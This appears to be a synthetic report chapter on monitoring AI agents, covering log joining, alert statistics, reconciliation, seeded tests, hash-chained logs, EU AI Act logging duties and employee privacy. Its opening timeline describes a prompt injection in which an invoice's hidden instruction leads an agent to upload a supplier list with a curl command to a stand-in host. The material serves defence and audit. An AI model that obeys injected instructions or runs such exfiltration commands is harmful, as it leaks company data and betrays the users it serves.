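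| 10:00:05 | Model gateway | "Summarise last month's invoices" | The recorded request doesn't ask for an upload |
| 10:00:08 | MCP gateway | `get_invoices`, with that token | Someone with the token requested the invoices |
| 10:00:09 | MCP gateway | Result includes an instruction to send the supplier list to `collect.example` | The server returned the hidden instruction |
| 10:00:11 | Model gateway | Prompt includes the same instruction | The instruction reached the model |
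| 10:00:13 | Model gateway | Model proposes `curl -T suppliers.csv https://collect.example/in` | The model proposed the upload after receiving the instruction |
| 10:00:14 | Device sensor | Agent program starts a shell, which starts `curl` | The command ran on the laptop |
| 10:00:15 | Device sensor | `curl` opens `suppliers.csv`, connects to an outside address and sends 48,210 bytes | Data left the laptop, very probably the supplier list |

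The token's hash links the first entry to the MCP call. A trace identifier can link that call to the model query if the agent program adds it to both, and the matching invoice text confirms the link. The trace probably ends at the shell, because `curl` doesn't add a `traceparent` header by default. To connect the model's proposal to the upload, the analyst has to match process ancestry, times and arguments, as AgentSight does.

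Together, the entries strongly suggest that the instruction hidden in the invoice hijacked the agent, because the employee asked for something else and the upload went to the address in that instruction. But the order of events doesn't prove that the instruction caused the upload. The analyst could test this by running the session several times in a sandbox, with and without the instruction. The case would be much stronger if the model proposed the upload only when the instruction was present.

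Without the sensor's records, the analyst couldn't tell whether the command ran or a hook stopped it. The analyst would also need the model gateway's records to rule out that the employee had asked for the upload.

### Combining two alerts

Joined records also let a company raise an alarm only when two detectors flag the same session. In a hypothetical example, 1 session in 10,000 is harmful, so 1,000,000 sessions include 100 harmful ones. A gateway alert has 90% recall and a 1% false positive rate, both measured per session. A device alert has 80% recall and a 2% false positive rate, and its errors are independent of the gateway alert's.

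| Alarm rule | Harmful sessions flagged | Harmless sessions flagged | Chance that an alarm is true |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gateway alert alone | 90 | 9,999 | 0.9% |
| Both alerts | 72 | 200 | 26% |
| Either alert | 98 | 29,797 | 0.3% |

The same result follows from Bayes' rule in terms of odds. The odds of harm start at 1 to 9,999. Each alert multiplies them by its recall divided by its false positive rate:

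(1 / 9,999) × (0.90 / 0.01) × (0.80 / 0.02) ≈ 0.36

Odds of 0.36 to 1 equal a probability of 0.36 / 1.36, or about 26%. Requiring the second alert cuts the number of alarms analysts review from about 10,000 to 272, but recall falls from 90% to 72%. A company could keep the other gateway alerts in a lower-priority queue instead of discarding them.

In practice, the alerts are unlikely to be fully independent. A large but legitimate year-end export might trigger the gateway alert because it contains customer data, and the device alert because it sends many files. The next table keeps the 72 true alarms and changes only how often the device alert also flags harmless sessions that the gateway has flagged.

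| Gateway's false alarms that the device alert also flags | Harmless sessions flagged by both | Chance that a joint alarm is true |
|---|---|---|
| 2% (independent) | 200 | 26% |
| 10% | 1,000 | 6.7% |
| 30% | 3,000 | 2.3% |
| 100% | 9,999 | 0.7% |

The device alert's overall false positive rate can be 2% in every row. In the last row, both alerts firing is slightly weaker evidence of harm than the gateway alert alone, because the device alert fires on all of the gateway's false alarms but only 80% of its true ones.

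Dependence between the alerts matters far less for the harmful sessions. If one alert catches 90 of the 100 harmful sessions and the other catches 80, both must flag between 70 and 80 of the same sessions. With 200 joint false alarms, between 26% and 29% of joint alarms would be true.

A bad join can have a similar effect to dependence. Suppose employees share an address and the join can't separate their sessions, so each session receives its own device alerts and those of four unrelated harmless sessions. A harmless session then has a 1 − 0.98⁵, or 9.6%, chance of receiving at least one device alert. The chance that a joint alarm is true falls from 26% to about 7%, although neither detector has changed.

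A company can measure the overlap by taking a random sample of the gateway's false alarms, joining them to the device records, and counting how many also have a device alert. If 60 of 200 do, the company should use 30% in the calculation instead of the 2% from the device alert's own test.

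## What the combined records can assure

A company that has joined its gateway, identity and device records may want to tell a customer or regulator that it monitors its agents. Assurance is justified confidence that such a statement is true, on grounds that others can check. "We monitor our agents" is too vague to check because it combines four claims, and any one of them can be true while the others are false.

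| Claim | How to check it | How it can fail on its own |
|---|---|---|
| Coverage: the records contain the relevant actions | Compare them with the logs of the systems acted upon | An agent changes a database through its shell |
| Detection: the detectors flag risky actions | Plant harmless imitations of incidents | The gateway logs an upload but raises no alarm |
| Integrity: nobody has altered the records | Verify hashes and signatures | An intruder deletes entries |
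| Response: alerts lead to timely action | Time the response in drills and real incidents | Responders understand an alert but let the agent continue, as OpenAI's did on 27 June |

Each claim also needs a scope. For example, an auditor can test the claim "In September, our gateway recorded at least 98% of the changes that agents made to the invoice database" because it specifies a period, a system and a number.

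### Reconciling two logs

A company can check coverage by comparing the gateway's log with the log of a system on which agents act, and investigating every action that appears only in the system's log.

Suppose agents and employees both change records in an invoice database. In one week, the database logs 2,400 changes, and the MCP gateway logs 2,310 calls that should each have made one change. An analyst pairs the entries by time, account and invoice number.

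| Where the entry appears | Number |
|---|---|
| Both logs | 2,280 |
| Database log only | 120 |
| Gateway log only | 30 |

Of the 120 changes found only in the database log, employees made 70 in the ordinary accounting program. An agent's script made another 35 through the database's command-line program. Ten went through the gateway but weren't matched because a clock was wrong. The analyst can't explain the last five.

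Agents therefore made at least 2,325 changes (2,280 + 10 + 35), and 2,290 of them, or 98.5%, went through the gateway. If agents also made the five unexplained changes, the share was 98.3%. Of the 30 calls found only in the gateway's log, ten belong to the mistimed changes, and the other 20 failed or changed nothing.

These percentages cover all changes, not just risky ones. But if the database log is complete and the matches are correct, any risky change that bypassed the gateway must be among the 35 from the script or the five unexplained ones, and someone can read all 40.

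Reconciliation works only for actions that the target system logs. Many databases log changes but not reads by default, so an agent could copy the whole supplier list without leaving an entry to compare. The company also usually can't get logs from outside systems, such as the file-sharing service to which a hijacked agent uploads a list. For these actions, it has to use the device sensor's records instead. If an agent uses an employee's account, the analyst may also mistakenly include its changes in the 70 attributed to employees.

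A harmful effect can also go unnoticed when the records match. An analyst who compared only the number of emails requested and sent would have missed the hidden copies made by `postmark-mcp`, so reconciliation has to compare details such as recipients too.

Comparing the logs doesn't reveal actions missing from both. Statisticians estimate the number of such actions with capture–recapture, a method developed for counting animals. Suppose device sensors record 900 uploads by agents, the model gateway records 800, and 760 appear in both logs. Together the logs contain 940 different uploads. If each log misses uploads independently of the other, the estimated total is 900 × 800 / 760, or about 947, so about seven uploads are in neither. But uploads by an agent on an employee's home computer would appear in neither log, so the true total is probably higher.

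### Seeded tests

A company can check detection by planting harmless imitations of incidents, called seeded tests, in its own systems. To imitate the invoice theft, it could create a list of invented suppliers, hide an instruction in a test invoice and use a web address it owns. It then counts how many tests trigger an alarm. If the agent ignores the hidden instruction, the detector is not tested, so the company may prefer to script the upload itself.

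If the detector misses a share *p* of such incidents, the probability that it catches 60 in a row is (1 − *p*)⁶⁰. At a miss rate of 4.9%, that probability is 5%. A company with no misses in 60 independent tests can therefore say with 95% confidence that its miss rate is below about 5%. When there are no misses, dividing 3 by the number of tests gives nearly the same upper limit.

| Tests | Misses | Upper limit on the miss rate, with 95% confidence |
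|---|---|---|
| 10 | 0 | 26% |
| 60 | 0 | 4.9% |
| 60 | 1 | 7.7% |
| 300 | 0 | 1.0% |

The calculation assumes independent tests. If a company repeats 12 scenarios five times each and the detector always gives the same result for the same scenario, the 60 runs count as only 12 independent tests. With no misses, the upper limit is 22%.

The limit also applies only to the kinds of incident tested, so 60 imitation uploads don't measure how well the detector catches deletions. If the company instead imitates 20 uploads, 20 deletions and 20 changes to access rights, and the detector catches them all, the upper limit on the miss rate for each kind is about 14%. The threat lists published by OWASP and MITRE can help a company choose what to imitate, but one test per entry isn't enough, because an entry may cover several kinds of attack.

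What a test measures also depends on where it starts. Tests that send calls straight to the gateway measure only the detector, while tests that start on ordinary laptops and use the same routes as real agents measure coverage and detection together. Neither kind measures false positives, so a detector that flags every call would pass them all. A company that publishes its miss rate should also publish its false positive rate.

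### Hash chains and signatures

An intruder who gains control of a gateway may try to edit its log. A hash-chained log makes such edits visible because each entry's hash also depends on the hash before it:

```
h1 = SHA-256(entry 1)
h2 = SHA-256(h1 + entry 2)
h3 = SHA-256(h2 + entry 3)
```

Here the plus sign means the program joins two pieces of text before it computes the hash. If someone changes entry 2, `h2` no longer matches, and neither does any later hash.

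An intruder who controls the whole log could alter an entry and recompute all the later hashes, or delete the newest entries, leaving a shorter but valid chain. To guard against this, the gateway can regularly send its latest hash to a separate system. If it does this every hour, an intruder who takes over at 14:20 can rewrite the entries made since 14:00, but any change to earlier ones will conflict with the stored hash.

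The gateway can also sign its entries with a secret key, so that anyone with the matching public key can check who signed them. But if the secret key is on the gateway, an intruder with administrator rights can sign false entries. OpenAI's package store had this weakness, and agents stole the key it used to sign credentials. Keeping the key in a separate device or service that never releases it makes theft harder, though an intruder might still get that device or service to sign false entries during the break-in.

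Even an intact chain doesn't prove that the log is complete. Numbering the entries reveals whether someone has removed one, but not whether there was an action that the gateway never logged, such as a shell command.

A valid chain can also contain false information. If OpenAI had hashed and signed the transcripts its agents spoofed, that would only have proved that nobody changed them afterwards. To check whether an entry was true when the gateway wrote it, an investigator needs a second record from a source the same intruder didn't control.

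### Time to detect and time to stop

Time to detect is the time between a harmful action and the first alert about it that reaches a responder. Time to stop is the time between that alert and the point when the agent can do no further harm. Stopping an agent may require ending its process, revoking its tokens and cancelling any scripts it has scheduled.

Suppose an agent wrongly deletes a record every five seconds. If detection takes 20 minutes and stopping it takes another ten, the agent deletes 360 records. Halving the time to detect would save 120 of them, and halving the time to stop would save 60.

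How quickly the company must respond depends on the harm. In the invoice timeline, the supplier list left the laptop two seconds after the model proposed the upload, too soon for anyone to stop it. The company needs an automatic block for such actions, but a response within half an hour may be acceptable when the damage is slow.

Average stopping times can mislead. If responders stop nine agents in ten minutes each and the tenth after three days, the average is more than seven hours and the median is ten minutes. A customer learns more from the share of agents stopped within the deadline and the time taken in the slowest case. Seeded tests avoid the bias in reported delays, because the company knows when each test began and can count the misses. Some tests should start at night or at a weekend, when fewer people are watching.

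A company can have respectable rates of coverage, detection and response and still have only modest protection. Suppose that 95% of risky actions enter the records, the detectors flag 90% of those, and responders stop 80% of the flagged ones in time. The company then stops about 68% of all risky actions (0.95 × 0.90 × 0.80).

### What the EU AI Act requires

The EU AI Act requires logs only for high-risk systems. These include the uses listed in Annex III, such as recruitment and credit scoring, and AI in certain products covered by the safety laws in Annex I, such as toys and lifts. The requirement probably covers an agent that ranks job applicants but not one that summarises invoices.

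The Act divides duties between providers, who develop a system and put it on the market, and deployers, who use it at work. artificialintelligenceact.eu's *Article 12* sets out the main logging rule, which requires high-risk systems to be technically able to log events automatically throughout their lifetime. The logged events must help identify risks and substantial modifications, and allow the provider and deployer to monitor the system. The article lists minimum log contents, such as the start and end of each use, only for remote biometric identification. It doesn't specify whether an agent's log must contain prompts, tool arguments or shell commands.

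Providers must keep these logs for at least six months, according to Mishcon de Reya's *Article 19 Automatically Generated Logs*. The European Commission's *Article 26* sets the same minimum for deployers. Both duties cover only logs under the organisation's control. If the agent runs on a provider's machines, those logs may be a small part of the evidence.

Article 26 also comes closest to a rule on response. A deployer must have competent people oversee the system and must monitor its operation. If the deployer has reason to think that using the system as instructed may present a risk, as the Act defines that term, it must suspend use and, "without undue delay", inform the provider or distributor and the authorities. It must report serious incidents immediately.

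*EU AI Act deployer evidence gaps SMEs will miss*, published by the privacy professionals' association IAPP, argues that a deployer must be able to show evidence of how it monitors and logs each system. According to the article, many deployers wrongly treat these duties as the vendor's job. The provider must explain how to collect, store and interpret the logs, according to datenschutz notizen's *AI logging under the EU AI Act*. Authorities can also demand the logs from the provider.

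A company could comply with these three articles and still have little assurance in the sense used here, because none of them sets a maximum miss rate, requires reconciliation or mentions hash chains.

The duties don't apply yet because the European Union's *Regulation (EU) 2026/1744* (2026) postponed them to 2 December 2027 for Annex III systems and 2 August 2028 for Annex I systems. It appeared in the Official Journal on 24 July 2026, nine days before the Annex III duties would have started. Its stated reasons include delays in preparing technical standards and in setting up national bodies to assess systems. High-risk systems already on the market by the new dates fall under the rules only if their design changes significantly afterwards. Providers and deployers of such systems intended for public authorities must comply by 2 August 2030 in any case.

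Independent audit plays a limited part. The Act may require an outside body to assess biometric systems and products covered by Annex I, but providers of most other Annex III systems assess their own. The 2026 regulation adds a list of codes for the kinds of AI that an outside body may be qualified to assess, and one code explicitly includes agentic AI. These assessments examine whether the provider's system meets the Act's requirements, not whether a company that uses the system would notice a hijacked agent.

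### Standards and guidance in preparation

Technical standards could turn Article 12's general wording into specific requirements. The International Organization for Standardization (ISO) lists ISO/IEC 24970, a standard on logging in AI systems, as under publication. Smith (2026), in *Two standards, one architecture*, explains that European standards build on such international standards and connect them to the Act. A provider that follows a European standard officially recognised for this purpose can presume that it meets the corresponding legal requirement.

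The European draft is *AI trustworthiness framework* (2026), from the standards organisations CEN and CENELEC. It has clauses on deciding which events to log, reassessing that choice over time, and protecting the log and people's privacy. The draft is still open to comment and may change. iTeh Standards' *prEN 18229-1* gives a planned publication date of 30 May 2027, about six months before the Annex III duties begin.

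In the United States, Booth, Fisher and colleagues (2026) raise questions close to the integrity claim in NIST's *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*. They ask how agents can log their actions and intent in a "tamper-proof and verifiable manner", and how to link those actions to a person's authorisation. They also want to track where an agent's prompts and input data came from, which would help an investigator find a hidden instruction. Logging intent is the hardest of these aims, because a signature can prove what an agent wrote about its intent but not that the statement was accurate.

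The concept paper drew more than 600 formal responses, according to Galluzzo's *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity* (2026). NIST's National Cybersecurity Center of Excellence (NCCoE) has released a summary of them. NCCoE's *Software and SI Agent Identity and Authorization* lists the project as still soliciting comments, and the practice guide that Booth and colleagues plan has not yet been published. ("SI" stands for "super intelligence", the term that an executive order of 29 September 2026 directed federal agencies to use in place of "artificial intelligence".) The project's first phase covers agents inside a company but not external agents from untrusted sources, so it would offer little help to an organisation like Services Australia, whose portal was entered by another company's agent.

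NIST is also adapting SP 800-53, its catalogue of security controls, to AI. Its *SP 800-53 Control Overlays for Super Intelligence Systems COSIS* proposes separate sets of controls for single agents and for groups of agents. By 20 October 2026, however, the only outline NIST had released was for predictive AI.

Companies can't fill the gap with older frameworks alone. Errico and colleagues examined NIST's AI Risk Management Framework and two ISO management standards, ISO/IEC 27001 for information security and ISO/IEC 42001 for AI. They concluded that the ISO standards lack specific controls for monitoring agents' tool calls at run time and that NIST's framework doesn't specifically address the risks of those calls. A certificate under either ISO standard is therefore weak evidence for the coverage or detection claim unless the company has added its own controls and the auditor has tested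 them.

### The privacy objection

Prompts can reveal far more about employees than ordinary network logs. Someone may ask an agent to draft a request for sick leave, a complaint about a manager or a message to a trade union. Session records also show how fast people work and what mistakes they make. An employer might collect all this to catch hijacked agents and later use it to judge its staff. A thief who broke into the log would find it all in one place. Employees can rarely refuse the monitoring, but some may move their work to personal accounts, so heavier monitoring could reduce coverage.

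Data minimisation, collecting and keeping no more than the purpose requires, answers part of the objection. A detector can scan a full prompt but store only the tool call and its verdict unless it raises an alarm. If the detector misses an incident, however, investigators will not have the prompt. Errico and colleagues still list privacy-preserving agent operations as an open research problem.

Restricting access to the records addresses the fear that managers will read them. A company can let security analysts open a session only after an alarm, for a random check or with a second person's approval, and log each time they do. Employees still have to trust the company to follow these rules, so their representatives should be able to inspect the access log.

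Telling users about such limits makes them easier to enforce, since employees can't object to a breach of rules they have never seen. Under Article 26, employers must inform workers' representatives and the affected workers before using a high-risk system at the workplace. Annex III includes systems intended to monitor and evaluate workers' performance and behaviour, so an agent-monitoring tool used for that purpose could be high-risk. Where data-protection law requires an assessment of the effects on people's privacy, the deployer must use the provider's information about the system to carry it out. Telling employees that the company records everything doesn't mean they have consented, and it wouldn't make the recording proportionate.

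Retention limits reduce the temptation to reuse the records and the damage if someone steals them. The AI Act's six-month minimum doesn't give employers a general right to keep prompts, because it applies only to logs that a high-risk system generates, and data-protection law takes precedence over it. But deleting records early can destroy evidence. OpenAI took up to 54 days to find the Medicare breach in its records, and a company that deleted everything after 30 days couldn't have found it that way. One compromise is to delete most prompts after a few weeks and keep the tool calls for longer, with names replaced by codes.

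Deletion also conflicts with a simple hash chain, since nobody can verify an entry's hash without its text. If the company stores the text separately and puts only its hash into the chain, it can delete the text and the remaining hashes will still link together. It should also mix a random value into each text's hash and delete that value with the text. Otherwise, someone could guess a short prompt and check the guess against the hash.
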